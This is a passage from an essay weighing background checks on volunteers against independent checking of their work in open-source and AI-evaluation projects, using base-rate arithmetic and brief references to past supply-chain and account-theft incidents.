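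| | Flagged | Passed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hostile | 8 | 2 | 10 |
| Honest | about 500 | about 9,490 | 9,990 |
| All volunteers | about 508 | about 9,492 | 10,000 |

Only 1.6% of the people flagged are hostile. If the programmes turned away everyone flagged, they would lose about 62 honest volunteers for each hostile one they kept out, and two hostile people would still get in. The share of hostile people among those accepted would fall from one in 1,000 to about one in 4,700. Whether that justifies losing 500 honest volunteers depends on how much harm one hostile person could do.

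Most volunteers could probably do very little harm, because someone else reviews their work before anyone uses it. A few have much more power. Suppose 100 of the 10,000 volunteers later ask for sensitive access, such as the right to publish releases, and 5 of the 10 hostile people are among them because they joined to get that access. The same check would flag 4 hostile people and about 5 honest ones. Nearly half of the flags would be correct, and a programme could interview all nine people properly. It therefore makes much more sense to run the check when people ask for access than when they first volunteer.

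### Check the person or check the work?

The best argument for vetting people is that more review adds little against an attacker as skilled as Jia Tan, so the remaining option is to keep such a person off the project. Some harm also never appears in the work under review, since a volunteer who hands in excellent research may also be copying unpublished results for someone else.

Background checks are meant mainly to stop patient attackers, who are also the most likely to pass them. Checks don't stop someone from using an honest contributor's stolen account, as happened at LiteLLM. They would also be hard on volunteers with little public history, including many students.

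Checking the work also catches honest mistakes, which are surely far more common than sabotage. If a second person reruns an evaluation and gets a different score, the project benefits whether or not anyone meant harm. Reviewers don't have to accuse anyone. Kernel developers wrongly accused Aditya Pakki of bad faith when they could have just rejected his patches as poor.

Thorough checking takes time. Inspect Evals gave up thorough checks on new evaluations because it could not sustain them, and it describes its present checks on outside code as "fairly minimal". Requiring someone to repeat every result would halt most small projects. Projects could instead repeat only the results that would change a decision, such as whether a model is safe to release or whether to abandon a line of research.

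On balance, projects should normally rely on checking work, and should check people only for positions that let them bypass review or see confidential material. Even then, nobody should be able to publish a release or approve a dataset alone, since background checks will sometimes be wrong. LiteLLM's experience suggests that it should also be hard to steal several people's approvals at once, for instance by requiring each person to confirm with a separate physical key.

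Openness helps with checking because outsiders do some of it for free. Andres Freund, Demir and FutureSearch's engineer had no role in the projects whose attackers they exposed. However, Freund and FutureSearch each had a misbehaving machine to investigate, and a biased evaluation or an invented result would not cause that kind of symptom. For research, openness would have to include the data, logs and failed experiments as well as the code, so that outsiders could find discrepancies by repeating the work.

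Some of that material should stay private. Answers to dangerous questions about biology could help someone build a weapon, and a published test can end up in the training data of the models it is meant to measure. Projects could share such material with a few outside reviewers, but would again have to decide whom to trust.

Outsiders also need a reason to look for problems. Demir read the malicious pull request because he wanted contributions to show employers, and he would gain less from a project that accepts changes only from approved people. Inspect Evals still invites everyone to report faulty evaluations. If it and similar projects publicly credited those reports as they credit code, a student could build a record by finding other people's mistakes, without needing permission to change anything.
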